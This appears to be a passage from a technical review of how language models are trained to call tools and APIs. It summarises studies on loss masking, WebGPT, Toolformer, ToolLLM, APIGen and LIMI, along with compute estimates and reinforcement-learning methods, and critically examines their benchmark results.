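Zhang, Makhija and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Mask the Environment*, directly tested the effect of masking the responses. They fine-tuned Qwen3-4B and Qwen3-8B on 50,000 traces in which a stronger model, DeepSeek-V3.2, had worked at a computer's command line. About 45% of the tokens were responses from the computer. They trained one version of each model only on the requests and reasoning, and the other on the responses as well. Both versions then went through the same reinforcement learning, without any loss on responses. They were tested on Terminal-Bench 2.0, a set of 89 command-line tasks, with 16 attempts at each.

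| Model and stage | Measure | Responses masked, % | Responses trained on, % |
|---|---|---|---|
| 4B, after fine-tuning | pass@1 | 4.5 | 4.4 |
| 8B, after fine-tuning | pass@1 | 9.2 | 7.9 |
| 4B, after reinforcement learning | pass@1 | 5.6 | 7.2 |
| 4B, after reinforcement learning | pass@16 | 18.0 | 19.1 |
| 8B, after reinforcement learning | pass@1 | 12.3 | 11.0 |
| 8B, after reinforcement learning | pass@16 | 23.6 | 27.0 |

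Before fine-tuning, the models scored 1.2% and 2.7% on pass@1, so both kinds of training helped a lot and the mask made little difference at first. Each pass@1 score had a standard error of about half a point. That includes variation between attempts by the same model but not between training runs, so the 1.3-point gap at 8B is hard to interpret. After reinforcement learning, training on responses gave better results at 4B. At 8B it lowered the success rate of single attempts but raised the chance that at least one of 16 would succeed.

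In further tests, the 8B model solved no tasks when it was trained only on responses, which shows that they can't replace the requests as training targets. When Zhang and colleagues swapped in mismatched responses from other traces, pass@1 dropped from 7.9% to 3.7%, so the model seems to learn something from the link between a command and its effect.

Their explanation is that masking has a drawback. As a model trained only on requests and reasoning, it became worse than the original Qwen model at predicting what the computer would return. Choosing a good command presumably involves some idea of what it will do, so losing this ability could hurt later training. *ECHO* (2026) applies the same idea to reinforcement learning by adding a loss on terminal output. This adds little computation because the model processes those tokens anyway.

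This evidence doesn't settle whether training on responses leads a model to invent them. The benchmark measures completed tasks, and a model could complete the same number while making more false statements on the tasks it fails. A direct test would give the same tasks to the versions trained with and without the mask, and count the results they report that no server returned. Until someone runs that test, the mask is a sensible precaution for a developer who plans to stop after fine-tuning, since training on responses didn't improve either model's pass@1 at that stage.

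### WebGPT: learning from people

WebGPT, from 2021, avoided the problem by never putting a whole trace in the context. At each step, the wrapper gave GPT-3 a fresh context with the question, the text of the current page near the cursor and a summary of past actions. The model replied with one command. The wrapper carried it out and discarded the context, so the summary was the model's only record of what it had done.

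Each step of a human demonstration could therefore become a separate training example, with the summary as the input and the person's next command as the target. These were the commands:

| Command | Effect |
|---|---|
| Search, with a query | Sends the query to Microsoft's Bing and shows the results |
| Clicked on link, with a number | Opens the linked page |
| Find in page, with some text | Moves to the next place where the text occurs |
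| Quote, with some text | Saves the passage as a reference, if it is on the page |
| Scrolled down, Scrolled up | Moves through the page by one to three steps |
| Top | Returns to the start of the page |
| Back | Returns to the previous page |
| End: Answer | Stops browsing and moves on to the answer |
| End: Nonsense, Controversial | Stops without answering |

The wrapper ignored anything else the model wrote, but that output still counted toward the limit on actions, which was 100 in the tests. Browsing also ended when the model reached this limit or had saved enough text. The wrapper then showed the model the question and the saved quotes, and the model wrote an answer that cited them.

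Nakano and colleagues hired 56 contractors to produce most of the data, and the five most active provided about half of it. The contractors used a graphical version of the model's browser, with almost the same information and actions. They recorded 6,209 demonstrations, which took about 15 minutes each. Most of the questions came from ELI5, a Reddit forum where people ask for simple explanations. The wrapper removed links to Reddit and Quora from the search results so that the model couldn't copy existing answers.

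The first stage of training was behaviour cloning, which is fine-tuning on the commands that people chose. Even a model that imitated these people perfectly would produce answers only about as good as theirs, so a judge should prefer its answers to theirs about half the time.

To go further, Nakano and colleagues collected 21,548 comparisons, in which a contractor read two answers to the same question and chose the better one. They used about 16,000 of these to train a reward model, a second model that gives each answer a score r. The difference between two scores predicts which answer a person would choose:

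P(A preferred to B) = 1 / (1 + e^−(r_A − r_B))

A one-point lead means that a person would prefer the higher-scoring answer about 73% of the time. Doubling the number of demonstrations raised the cloned model's score by about 0.13, so a person would prefer its answer to the earlier model's only about 53% of the time.

The comparisons helped more. In rejection sampling, the model made 64 attempts at each question, and the system kept the one that the reward model scored highest. This requires no further training of the browsing model, but answering each question takes far more compute. People preferred the best of 64 to a single attempt by the same 175-billion-parameter model 68% of the time. Reinforcement learning against the same reward model gave a smaller gain.

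The best system combined behaviour cloning with rejection sampling. People preferred its answers to the demonstrators' 56% of the time, and to the highest-voted Reddit answers 69% of the time. For the Reddit comparison, the researchers removed the citations and gave newly hired judges much shorter instructions. Nakano and colleagues consider the comparison with the demonstrators more meaningful, because both sets of answers had references to check and were written in a similar style.

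The judges checked whether the quoted sources supported each claim but did no research of their own, so this is a less demanding test of truth than it sounds. Nakano and colleagues acknowledge that it rewards a model for picking quotes that a judge will find convincing, even if they don't represent the evidence fairly. On TruthfulQA, a set of questions designed to attract common misconceptions, 75% of the system's answers were true, and 54% were both true and informative. Some of its answers quoted highly unreliable sites.

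A few thousand demonstrations were enough to teach GPT-3 to use an unfamiliar browser competently. Choosing among many attempts then made its results better than the demonstrators'. Making many attempts is harmless when the system only searches and reads.

### Toolformer: learning from the model's own calls

Schick, Dwivedi-Yu and colleagues (2023), in *Toolformer*, tried to do without the human demonstrations. They started with ordinary web text and GPT-J, a model with 6.7 billion parameters, and gave it a calculator, a calendar, a Wikipedia search engine, a translator and a question-answering system. Their method has four steps:

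1. A prompt with a few handwritten examples gets GPT-J to insert tool calls into existing texts. The software samples several calls at the places where the model gives a high probability to starting one.
2. The software executes every call and records the result.
3. A filter keeps the calls whose results make the rest of the text easier to predict.
4. GPT-J trains on the original texts with the remaining calls and results inserted.

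The filter replaces the human judge. Take a text x_1, ..., x_n with a possible call at position i. Let z be some extra text placed in front of it, and measure how well the model predicts what comes after the call:

L_i(z) = −Σ w_(j−i) log p(x_j | z, x_1, ..., x_(j−1)), summed over j from i to n

Then compare the loss with and without the result:

L⁺ = L_i(call and result)

L⁻ = the smaller of L_i(nothing) and L_i(call without result)

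The filter keeps the call if L⁻ − L⁺ ≥ τ, where τ is a threshold chosen for each tool. L⁻ includes the call without its result because the wording of a question can itself reveal the answer, and the filter should not count that as help from the tool. The weights w fall from 1/3 for the first token after the call to 1/15 for the fifth and are zero after that, so a result counts only if it helps predict those five tokens.

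One text says "The Nile has an approximate length of 6,853 kilometers". GPT-J inserted a question about the length just before the number, and the tool returned "6,853 km". This lowered the loss by 2.08. In a sentence about "85 patients (23%)", the model had the calculator divide 85 by 23. The result was useless, and the loss rose by 0.02.

The filter isn't perfect. GPT-J searched Wikipedia for "fast train to success", a phrase from a web page, and got a passage about a pop song. That call scored 0.92, while a correct translation in another text scored 0.70. Schick and colleagues suggest that some such noise may be useful because it stops the model from always relying on what a tool returns.

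The results below are percentages of correct answers. The third column shows the fine-tuned model when the software prevented it from making calls.

| Benchmark | GPT-J | Toolformer without calls | Toolformer | GPT-3 (175 billion parameters) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| T-REx (missing facts) | 31.9 | 34.9 | 53.5 | 39.8 |
| ASDiv (maths problems) | 7.5 | 14.8 | 40.4 | 14.0 |
| Dateset (dates) | 3.9 | 5.9 | 27.3 | 0.8 |
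| Web Questions | 18.5 | 18.9 | 26.3 | 29.0 |
| TriviaQA | 43.9 | 46.7 | 48.8 | 65.9 |

Toolformer beat a model 25 times its size when one call could supply most of the answer, though much of its advantage came from the tools. On T-REx, it nearly always used the question-answering system, which is itself a language model fine-tuned to answer factual questions. On the last two benchmarks, the researchers turned that system off, so Toolformer had to rely on a simple Wikipedia search, and it scored well below GPT-3.

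Fine-tuning doubled GPT-J's score on the maths problems even when it couldn't use a calculator. Schick and colleagues suspect that training on many calculations and their results improved the model's arithmetic. They describe the training objective as standard language modelling, which would train the model to predict the results as well as the calls. If so, the higher score is another sign that training on responses teaches a model something about how the tool behaves.

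Toolformer only partly decides for itself when to use a tool. With ordinary decoding, it made a call on only 8.5% of the Web Questions. The researchers then had it start a call whenever the opening marker was among the ten most probable tokens, which raised the figure to 100%. They also allowed only one call per text, to keep the model from making calls forever.

That restriction rules out the loop described at the start of this report, and removing it would not have been enough to teach the model that loop. The software samples every call independently, so the training data contains no example in which one call uses the result of another. It includes nothing like looking up Springfield's number and then using it to request the weather, or following a search that returned nothing useful with a better one. Schick and colleagues list both gaps as limitations.

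Services that can change data pose another problem, because Toolformer executes each call before checking whether it was worth making. A rejected calculator call only uses computing time, but a rejected call to an API that creates records would leave a record behind. The filter also needs existing text that the call makes easier to predict, and it isn't clear what that text would be after a request to cancel an order.

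### Traces from a stronger model

A trace of a complete task can show how one request depends on the last response. Recording people is slow, so developers often have a stronger model produce the traces, as in the ReAct experiment, where PaLM-540B produced them for smaller models. *WebSailor* (Li, Zhang and Yin, 2025) uses this method for difficult web research. Its traces use two tools. One sends queries to a search engine and returns the titles, snippets and addresses of ten results for each query. The other opens pages and returns a summary suited to the model's stated goal. Special tokens separate the thoughts, actions and observations, and the mask excludes the observations from the loss.

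Open reasoning models such as QwQ-32B attempted the tasks. Li and colleagues then kept only traces that ended in the correct answer, contained more than five tool calls and were no longer than 32,000 tokens. Just over 2,000 examples were enough to prepare their models for reinforcement learning. Because the first condition checks only the final answer, a trace with a pointless or mistaken request in the middle can still pass, and the mask treats that request like any other.

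The reasoning in these traces was so long that it would have filled the context over dozens of calls, and Li and colleagues also worried that their model would copy its style. They discarded it, kept the actions and responses, and had another model write a short justification for each action. That model saw the earlier steps, the action and the response to the action. Seeing the response makes it easier to write a sensible justification, but it may let information from the response into a thought that comes before the request. Thoughts have a mask of 1, so a model could learn to state a result before it has received it. Masking the response would not prevent these leaks, but the instruction to write brief reasons for the action may prevent most of them.

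### What happens without the earlier requests and responses?

*Toolformer* treats each call separately, while in *WebSailor* each call follows a full history. In *Trajectory Supervision for Continual Tool-Use Learning in LLMs*, Reddy B, Chatterjee and Bhatta (2026) compared something close to these two arrangements in a small pilot, done as a course project. They fine-tuned two versions of Llama 3.1 8B Instruct on API-Bank, a dataset of conversations that include API calls. Both versions learned to write the next call, one with the earlier requests and responses in its context and the other with them removed.

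Training went through four groups of APIs in turn. After the last group, the version with the history got 56.9% of calls exactly right, averaged over the groups, and the version without it got 39.2%. This is how the 440 test examples came out:

| Outcome | History removed | History kept |
|---|---|---|
| Call exactly right | 172 | 251 |
| Right API, some parameters right | 74 | 54 |
| Right API, parameters wrong | 47 | 22 |
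| Wrong API | 102 | 12 |
| Malformed call or no call | 45 | 101 |

The biggest change was in choosing the API. Among calls the test software could read, the version with the history named the right API 96% of the time, compared with 74% for the other version.

Reddy B and colleagues give three reasons for caution about this result. They ran each version once, with a single random seed, so they can't estimate how much the scores would vary between runs. The version with the history also trained on 25.1% more tokens, because its examples were longer, and extra training text might help regardless of its content. In the test, the model predicts only the next call, given a correct record of everything before it. A model that gets 57% of single calls right could do much worse on a whole task, where it has to continue from its own mistakes.

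The comparison also doesn't isolate the effect of training, because the researchers removed the history from the test prompts as well as from the training examples. If the next call needs an identifier from an earlier response, the version without the history has no way to get it, however well it was trained. The result therefore depends at least partly on the information in the prompt at test time. To isolate the effect of training, both versions would need the full history at test time.

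The version with the history produced more than twice as many malformed or missing calls. Reddy B and colleagues suggest that longer prompts make it harder to get the format exactly right. Their software accepted only one notation and required an exact match, so some of these failures may have been minor.

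## How much data, compute and model size does it take?

The data, compute and model size required depend on what the developer wants the model to do. A programmer needs about a day to prepare data that teaches a model to make valid calls to one known API. To use an unfamiliar API from its documentation, a model seems to need practice with thousands of APIs, but other models can generate the practice examples. Long tasks require the most resources, because the developer must start with a capable model and the traces are hard to produce. Training on the finished traces takes little compute in every case.

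### Calls to known APIs

In 2023, open models, whose weights (trained parameter values) anyone can download, were far worse than GPT-4 at calling APIs. In *On the Tool Manipulation Capability of Open-source Large Language Models* (2023), Xu, Hong and colleagues tried to close this gap on eight tasks. Two of the tasks required the model to write a complete HTTP request as a command for curl, a standard program for sending requests.

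A developer wrote templates for each tool. One template pairs a question about a city's current weather with a GET request, leaving a gap in both for the city's name. Software filled the gaps from a list of values, turning 90 weather templates into 1,800 training examples. Xu and colleagues estimate that this work, including writing a few examples for the prompt, took one developer about a day per tool. They fine-tuned a single model on all 9,704 examples from the eight tasks, making eight passes over the data on four GPUs.

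These are success rates on five of the tasks for LLaMA-30B, a base model from Meta:

| Task | Documentation only, % | Three examples in the prompt, % | Fine-tuned, % | Fine-tuned, with examples and instructions, % |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenWeather | 39 | 78 | 100 | 100 |
| The Cat API | 49 | 84 | 94 | 94 |
| Home Search | 0 | 66 | 85 | 87 |
| Trip Booking | 0 | 45 | 87.5 | 85.8 |
| Google Sheets | 0 | 37.1 | 4.3 | 2.9 |

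The weather test used the same nine functions as the training examples, so it shows only that the model learned those nine. Home Search is slightly harder, because its test cases combined functions in ways that never appeared in training. The Cat API includes POST requests that add pictures to a user's favourites and DELETE requests that remove them, so a day's work was also enough for calls with side effects. The researchers checked the deletions by comparing the model's request with the correct one instead of sending it, because deleting the same picture twice would fail.

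The trained model did badly on Google Sheets. Xu and colleagues attribute this to the reasoning the task requires, such as working out which cell holds the price of beef. But the untrained model scored 37.1% with three examples in the prompt, so it already had some of the ability, and the training apparently suppressed it. Only 118 of the 9,704 training examples involved spreadsheets.

### Unfamiliar APIs

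A developer can't write templates for every API in advance, but can put an API's documentation in the context and train the model to work from it. In *ToolLLM*, Qin, Liang and colleagues (2023) built a dataset for this from RapidAPI, an API marketplace. They found 53,190 APIs and kept 16,464 after removing unreliable ones. ChatGPT read the documentation for a few related APIs at a time and wrote nearly 200,000 tasks that required those APIs. It then attempted the tasks by making real API calls. The final dataset has 126,486 successful traces containing 469,585 calls.

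Even GPT-4 often failed these tasks when it couldn't go back and retry, because one mistaken call tended to lead to more. The software therefore let ChatGPT abandon a step and try a different one from an earlier point. Going back restores the earlier context but doesn't undo changes on the server, so any record created in an abandoned attempt would still be there.

Qin and colleagues report that a LLaMA model fine-tuned on these traces did about as well as ChatGPT, and that it could use APIs it had never seen from their documentation alone. On a separate set of APIs, it matched a system designed for them. Since the APIs differ from one training example to the next, memorising any of them helps little, and the model presumably learns to read the documentation. A weakness of the evaluation is that ChatGPT also judged the results. It agreed with human annotators 87.1% of the time on whether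 a task was complete, and its errors could favour a model trained on ChatGPT's traces.

Such training doesn't always transfer well to other kinds of questions. *FireAct* (Chen, Shu and colleagues, 2023) fine-tuned GPT-3.5 to answer HotpotQA questions with a Google search tool. On similar questions written so that a direct search won't find the answer, the fine-tuned model scored 44.0%, compared with 40.8% for prompting. The training hardly carried over to yes/no and multiple-choice questions, even though the search tool was the same.

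### Executing the calls to find bad examples

A model that generates training data makes mistakes, and fine-tuning on that data would teach them to the next model. Mistakes in tool calls are easier to check for than mistakes in ordinary text, because software can execute the calls and record the results. Liu, Hoang and colleagues (2024) used this kind of check in *APIGen* to build a dataset of about 60,000 examples. They started with ToolLLM's 16,464 APIs and kept the 3,539 that passed their tests for working requests, usable documentation and at least one parameter. They added 134 Python functions and had several open models write user requests with matching calls.

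Each example had to pass three checks. To see what they catch, take the question about rain in Springfield, Illinois, where the right identifier is 742:

1. The format check parses the call and compares it with the API's description. It rejects a call to a function that doesn't exist.
2. The execution check sends the call. It rejects an identifier that the server doesn't recognise.
3. The semantic check gives the request, the call and the response to another language model, which judges whether they fit together. Only this check could reject 318, the identifier for Springfield, Missouri, and only if the response or the documentation reveals which city it is.

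Liu and colleagues generated 40,000 examples with each model. The results for two of them show how much the generator's quality matters:

| Outcome | DeepSeek-Coder (33 billion parameters) | DeepSeek-V2-Chat (236 billion parameters) |
|---|---|---|
| Failed the format check | 4,311 | 817 |
| Failed the execution check | 15,496 | 3,359 |
| Failed the semantic check | 6,424 | 2,165 |
| Passed all three | 13,769 (34%) | 33,659 (84%) |

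A model with 6.7 billion parameters, fine-tuned on APIGen data, came sixth on the function-calling benchmark BFCL, ahead of GPT-4o, and one with 1.3 billion parameters beat GPT-3.5 Turbo. However, each APIGen example contains only one model output, which may include several calls but none that depends on an earlier response. The results are therefore good evidence about writing calls but little evidence about acting on responses.

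As with Toolformer's filter, executing every call is safe only when the calls just read data.

### Finishing whole tasks

Chen and colleagues trained models on complete traces in which GPT-4 searched, read the result and searched again. Fine-tuning on 500 successful traces raised Llama-2-7B's score on HotpotQA from 14.8% to 26.2% and GPT-3.5's from 31.4% to 39.2%. Both remained below GPT-4, which scored 42.0% when prompted with worked examples. The fine-tuned GPT-3.5 took 2.7 seconds per question, compared with 9.0 for the prompted version, because its prompt no longer needed those examples.

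These tasks take only a few searches. Xiao, Jiang and colleagues (2025), in *LIMI*, claim that even fewer traces are enough for much longer tasks. They collected 60 requests from developers and researchers and generated 18 more from code changes on GitHub. Four PhD students worked through them with GPT-5 at a command line, repeating each request until it succeeded. The 78 traces average 42,400 tokens, and the longest has 152,000.

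The fine-tuned model was GLM-4.5, which has 355 billion parameters and was already designed for tool use. Fine-tuning raised its average score on AgencyBench, a set of ten long programming and research tasks, from 45.1% to 73.5%. Fine-tuning on 10,000 traces from another dataset instead raised it to only 47.8%. The difference between the two results is 25.7 percentage points, or 54% in relative terms, though one passage of the paper gives it as 53.7 percentage points.

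This striking result is probably narrower than it looks. The training traces came from the same command-line wrapper that the researchers used for testing, while the 10,000 others did not. The paper also illustrates its training requests with a five-stage project to build the board game Gomoku, which is one of the ten test tasks. If that request was among the 78, the model had already practised one of the tasks it was tested on.

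The gains on other benchmarks are much smaller. Xiao and colleagues report that the average over all their tests rose from 43.0% to 57.2%, but averaging the individual scores in the way that reproduces the 43.0% gives 54.0% for the fine-tuned model. Without AgencyBench, the average of the other seven scores rose from 42.1% to 45.6%. Without the command-line tools, the average on the same seven tests rose from 48.7% to 49.7% (the paper reports 50.0%), so both models did better on these tests without the tools. The paper credits the tools with an improvement of 7.2 points, but it gets this by comparing an average that includes AgencyBench with one that doesn't.

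*LIMI* suggests that a few dozen excellent traces can adapt an already capable model to a particular wrapper and kind of work. Traces don't make up for a weaker starting model. Li and colleagues applied the same method, about 2,000 traces followed by reinforcement learning, to models of four sizes. On BrowseComp, a set of very hard web research questions, the models with 3, 7, 32 and 72 billion parameters scored 3.3%, 6.7%, 10.5% and 12.0%. OpenAI's Deep Research scored 51.5% at the time.

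### Where the traces come from

Human demonstrations are the most expensive source of training data. WebGPT's took about 15 minutes each, or more than 1,500 hours in total. Recordings of ordinary browsing would be far more plentiful, but according to *Scalable Behaviour Cloning on Browser Using via Skill Distillation* (2026), they make poor training data because they are full of misclicks and idle waits, contain personal text, and record clicks at positions that move when the page changes. The paper's proposed system turns the recordings into written instructions, such as how to recognise the required fields in a form, and puts the relevant ones in the model's context instead of fine-tuning the model.

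Training traces usually come from a stronger model, but a model can also learn from its own successful attempts, as Toolformer did. This requires the model to succeed sometimes. A model that succeeds once in a hundred attempts would need about 500,000 attempts to collect 5,000 successful traces, and each attempt that involves a live service might change something on that service.

Recent open-weight models rely heavily on simulated services, which avoid that problem. A program can reset a simulated shop after every attempt and check its database to see whether the right order went through. The *LongCat-Flash-Thinking-2601 Technical Report* (2026) describes simulated environments in 33 subject areas and keeps only traces that end in the intended state. *Nanbeige4.2-3B* (2026) combines live MCP services, tools rewritten in Python and tools whose responses another language model generates to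 train a model with 3 billion parameters. *ASTRA* (2026) also mixes real and simulated tools, starting from 19,036 tool descriptions. *Unlocking Implicit Experience* (2026) goes furthest, generating both the tools and the traces from ordinary text.

A made-up response may differ from what the real service would send. *ToolSpace* (2026) ranks traces by how real they are and puts those with synthetic tools last. It keeps calls from these last traces only if the name and format match a real tool.

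| Dataset | Size | Services |
|---|---|---|
| Chen and colleagues, 2023 | 500 traces | Live Google search |
| *ToolLLM*, 2023 | 126,486 traces | 16,464 live APIs |
| Liu and colleagues, 2024 | About 60,000 single-output examples | 3,673 executable APIs and functions |
| Xiao and colleagues, 2025 | 78 traces, about 3.3 million tokens | Command line |
| Toucan-1.5M, 2025, as *ToolSpace* describes it | 1.5 million traces | Over 2,000 tools on 495 real MCP servers |
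| *Solar Open Technical Report* (2026) | 161,608 examples, about 1.3 billion tokens | Simulated |

The Solar Open developers report that training on their simulated data alone, without dedicated reinforcement learning, gave a score of 60 points on Tau²-Bench, a test of customer-service tasks. That is a respectable result for imitation, though Tau²-Bench is also a simulation.

Developers disagree about what to do with failed calls inside a successful trace. *EnvFactory* (2026) makes every step a separate example and drops the steps with failed calls. The LongCat developers leave a failed call in the context but give it a loss mask of 0, so their model learns what to write after the error message without learning to write the bad call. This seems the better choice for a model that will meet errors in use.

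### How small can the model be?

Before any fine-tuning, a model's pre-training matters at least as much as its size. Xu and colleagues tested 27 models with three examples in the prompt. These are some of the results:

| Model | Parameters, billions | Pre-training tokens, billions | OpenWeather, % | Home Search, % |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OPT | 1.3 | 300 | 18 | 0 |
| Pythia | 1.4 | 300 | 37 | 4 |
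| Pythia | 12 | 300 | 53 | 12 |
| StarCoder | 15.5 | 1,000 | 91 | 82 |
| LLaMA | 65 | 1,400 | 90 | 84 |
| BLOOMZ | 176 | 366 | 58 | 36 |

The two Pythia models were trained on the same data, so the difference between them comes from size. StarCoder, which was trained on source code, matched a LLaMA model four times as large. BLOOMZ, the largest open model in the test, did worse than both.

Fine-tuning helps small models most when the task is a single call. APIGen's 1.3-billion-parameter model could beat GPT-3.5 Turbo on BFCL, whereas most of the models of about that size that Shahriar and Mastoi tested without fine-tuning rarely produced readable JSON. Searching in several steps is harder to teach small models. In *FireAct*, fine-tuning raised Llama-2-7B's score by 77% in relative terms, but the model still scored below a GPT-3.5 that had only been prompted. The smallest WebSailor model answered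 only about one in 30 BrowseComp questions correctly. These models date from 2023 to 2025, and the size needed for each task will keep changing because newer small models start from better pre-training.

### A compute estimate

A common rule estimates the compute for training as

C = 6 × N × D

where N is the number of parameters and D is the number of tokens the model processes. Reading a token takes about two operations per parameter, and working out how to adjust the parameters takes about four more.

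Suppose a developer fine-tunes a model with 7 billion parameters for three passes over 5,000 traces of 4,000 tokens. That makes 60 million tokens, so

C = 6 × (7 × 10⁹) × (6 × 10⁷) ≈ 2.5 × 10¹⁸ operations

A GPU that sustains 4 × 10¹⁴ operations a second finishes this in 6,300 seconds, or an hour and 45 minutes. The loss mask doesn't shorten the time, because the model still has to process the tokens it only reads.

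Here is the same calculation with other amounts of text:

| What the 7-billion-parameter model trains on | Tokens | Operations | Time on one such GPU |
|---|---|---|---|
| LIMI's 78 traces, once | 3.3 million | 1.4 × 10¹⁷ | 6 minutes |
| The 5,000 traces above, three times | 60 million | 2.5 × 10¹⁸ | 1.75 hours |
| Solar Open's simulated data, once | 1.3 billion | 5.5 × 10¹⁹ | 38 hours |
| Pre-training text | 2 trillion | 8.4 × 10²² | 6.7 years |

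Pre-training takes about 33,000 times as much compute as fine-tuning on the 5,000 traces, so almost all of the compute for a tool-using model of this kind goes into making the underlying language model.

The rule doesn't cover memory, or the computation needed to relate each token to the earlier ones, which is minor at 4,000 tokens but substantial at LIMI's 42,400. To adjust every parameter of Llama-2-7B, Chen and colleagues needed four GPUs with 80 GB of memory each. They ran most of their experiments with LoRA, which trains a small number of added parameters and leaves the original ones unchanged. With LoRA, a single RTX 4090, a consumer graphics card, processed 5.4 examples a second, enough to go through 500 traces once in about a minute and a half. The LoRA model scored lower, at 26.2% compared with 30.2% for full fine-tuning.

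The larger omission is the work before and after the successful training run. At APIGen's pass rates, 5,000 usable examples would take between 6,000 and 14,500 attempts, depending on the generator, and long traces fail more often than single calls. Developers also repeat training runs to correct mistakes, like the empty loss mask that Luv Verma describes, or to try other settings. They then have to test the model on whole tasks, and the Terminal-Bench comparison in the last section took 1,424 runs for each version of the model. For a small project, making the traces and testing the model can easily cost more than the training.

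### Does fine-tuning mostly teach a format?

Such small datasets suggest that a model learns how web requests work during pre-training, and that fine-tuning only teaches it which notation to use and when.

Several results are consistent with this. Chen and colleagues found that Llama models couldn't learn the ReAct format from 100 or 200 traces, but got reasonable scores with 500. GPT-3.5, a stronger model, reached about 35% with 100 traces and gained little after 200. LLaMA-30B went from 0% to 66% on Home Search with three examples in the prompt and no additional training. LIMI's gains nearly disappeared when the researchers removed the command-line tools.

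Other results suggest that fine-tuning teaches more than notation. Before fine-tuning, LLaMA-30B failed 61% of the weather requests. Xu and colleagues found that its output wouldn't execute for 7% of the requests, called the wrong function for 22%, and filled in the wrong values for 32%. Fine-tuning removed all of these failures, so the model must also have learned facts about that API.

Traces can also teach a model how to react to bad results. In one test, Chen and colleagues made the search tool return a random result half the time. The prompted GPT-3.5's score fell from 31.4% to 22.6%, while the fine-tuned version's fell only from 39.2% to 37.2%. They suggest the fine-tuned version held up better because its training traces included GPT-4 recovering from useless searches.

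Zhang and colleagues came closest to directly testing whether a model mostly learns format from the traces. They trained a model on mismatched responses, which keep the format but break the link between a command and its effect. The model gained only 1 point over its score before fine-tuning, compared with 5.2 points when the responses were correct. If it mostly learned format, the mismatched traces should have worked nearly as well. But the mismatches may also have done some harm, so the comparison probably understates what format contributes.

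Li and colleagues found something similar on long tasks. A 32-billion-parameter model trained by reinforcement learning without first imitating traces ended up clearly worse and made far fewer tool calls. It apparently didn't discover long search strategies by itself.

The claim is roughly right for single calls by a capable model, but it gets weaker as tasks get longer. Part of the disagreement is about what counts as "already present". The base models that Oh and colleagues tested usually failed BFCL's multi-step tasks on a single attempt, but solved about half of them at least once in 32 attempts. Making those rare successes common is useful, whether or not it counts as adding a new ability.

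### Can a developer withhold tool use from an open-weight model?

Leaving tool-use traces out of a model's training would hardly delay people who want to connect it to ordinary APIs once its weights are published. The APIGen and ToolLLM datasets are free to download, training takes hours, and a consumer graphics card is enough for a 7-billion-parameter model. Many users wouldn't need to train anything, because a prompt and a wrapper program are enough to have the model make requests and act on the responses.

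The company could go further and remove source code and API documentation from the pre-training data. That would make the model worse at programming, which is one of the main reasons people want such models. Users could also put the documentation in the context or train the model further on the missing data.

Long tasks leave more room for control, because the quality of the underlying model limits performance on them. Training on 78 traces can't turn a weak 3-billion-parameter model into a reliable researcher. A company can keep its most capable model private and restrict what customers do with the outputs. But if it publishes a capable model, the traces are easy to copy. LIMI's whole dataset, which Xiao and colleagues released, is 3.3 million tokens, about as much text as a few dozen novels. Model size gives some protection, since a model with 355 billion parameters takes up 355 GB even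 at one byte per parameter and needs several GPUs to run. Most home computers can't run it, but a small company could rent the hardware.

This argument is based on cost figures, which make it unlikely that others would need much work to restore tool use to a capable model trained without it. A direct test would be to train and publish such a model, then measure that work. Whoever restores the ability also writes the wrapper, so the original developer can't rely on the wrapper to limit calls to an allowed list or require the user's approval either. The remaining controls belong to the services that receive the requests, which can require an account or an API key before they respond.

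## What does reinforcement learning add?

Developers usually choose training traces because they ended well, so the traces contain few mistakes. A model fine-tuned on them gets little practice at recovering from the mistakes it still makes in use. In *One Policy Is Enough*, for example, Dariani, Wu and colleagues (2026) taught models to use chemistry tools with traces in which every call succeeded. FireAct's traces, however, did show GPT-4 recovering from useless searches.

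Imitation also optimises for good answers only indirectly. Fine-tuning makes every unmasked token in a trace more probable, regardless of how much it matters. Writing 318 instead of 742 ruins the weather answer, while opening with "It is raining" instead of "Yes" does no harm, but the loss penalises both as departures from the trace. Nakano and colleagues noted in 2021 that training WebGPT on demonstrations doesn't directly optimise the quality of its answers.

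Reinforcement learning scores the model's own attempts at a task instead of giving it a trace to copy. The model makes these attempts in the same loop it will use after training, so it practises dealing with its own mistakes. The training software then adjusts the model to make attempts like the high-scoring ones more likely.

### One round of training

1. The software gives the model the same task several times. It samples tokens at random, so the attempts differ.
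2. A program scores each attempt, for example 1 if the final answer is right and 0 if it is wrong.
3. The software compares each score with the rest of the group to get the attempt's advantage.
4. It makes the tokens the model wrote more probable if the advantage is positive, and less probable if it is negative.
5. The adjusted model attempts the next tasks.

Li and colleagues, who trained WebSailor, use the group-relative advantage, which for attempt i is

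A_i = (R_i − mean of the group's scores) / (standard deviation of the group's scores)

These are the results for some groups of four:

| Scores | Advantages |
|---|---|
| 1, 0, 0, 1 | +1, −1, −1, +1 |
| 1, 0, 0, 0 | +1.73, −0.58, −0.58, −0.58 |
| 0, 0, 0, 0 | No signal |
| 1, 1, 1, 1 | No signal |
| 1.00, 0.99, 0.99, 1.00 | +1, −1, −1, +1 |

When all the scores are equal, none differs from the mean, so the software has no reason to prefer any attempt. In its simplest form, the update minimises

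L = −A Σ m_t log p(x_t | earlier tokens)

With an advantage of 1, this is the fine-tuning loss applied to the model's own trace, with the same loss mask m_t. With an advantage of −1, training lowers the probability of those tokens instead. Most methods also limit how much one batch of attempts can change the model. With a limit of 20%, for example, raising the probability of "742" from 0.3 to 0.36 improves the training objective, but raising it further adds nothing.

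The last row of the table shows a weakness of dividing by the standard deviation. If every attempt in a group is equally correct, the division gives a trivial difference in behaviour as much weight as the difference between success and failure. Cursor left the division out for this reason when it trained a programming model, according to its *Composer 2 Technical Report* (2026).

### Why imitation usually comes first

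If a model succeeds with probability p, the chance that a group of n attempts contains both successes and failures is

1 − pⁿ − (1 − p)ⁿ

With 16 attempts per group and a success rate of 20%, 97% of groups give a signal. That share falls to 15% at a success rate of 1%, and to 1.6% at 0.1%. A model that can't yet write valid calls almost never finishes a task, so nearly all of its attempts are wasted. A short imitation stage raises the success rate enough for reinforcement learning to work. Li and colleagues say they fine-tuned WebSailor first partly because rewards on their difficult web questions were close to zero at the start.

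Dariani and colleagues compared the two stages directly. Their questions took between two and six calls, many of which needed a value from an earlier response. For reinforcement learning, a program scored the model's calls against a reference list. A separate language model then judged the final answers to 200 test questions:

| Training | Qwen-2.5-7B, % correct | Llama-3.1-8B, % correct | Qwen3-4B, % correct |
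|---|---|---|---|
| None | 54.0 | 24.5 | 53.0 |
| Imitation only | 65.5 | 69.5 | 65.5 |
| Reinforcement learning only | 60.0 | 62.5 | 57.0 |
| Imitation, then reinforcement learning | 68.5 | 64.0 | 68.0 |

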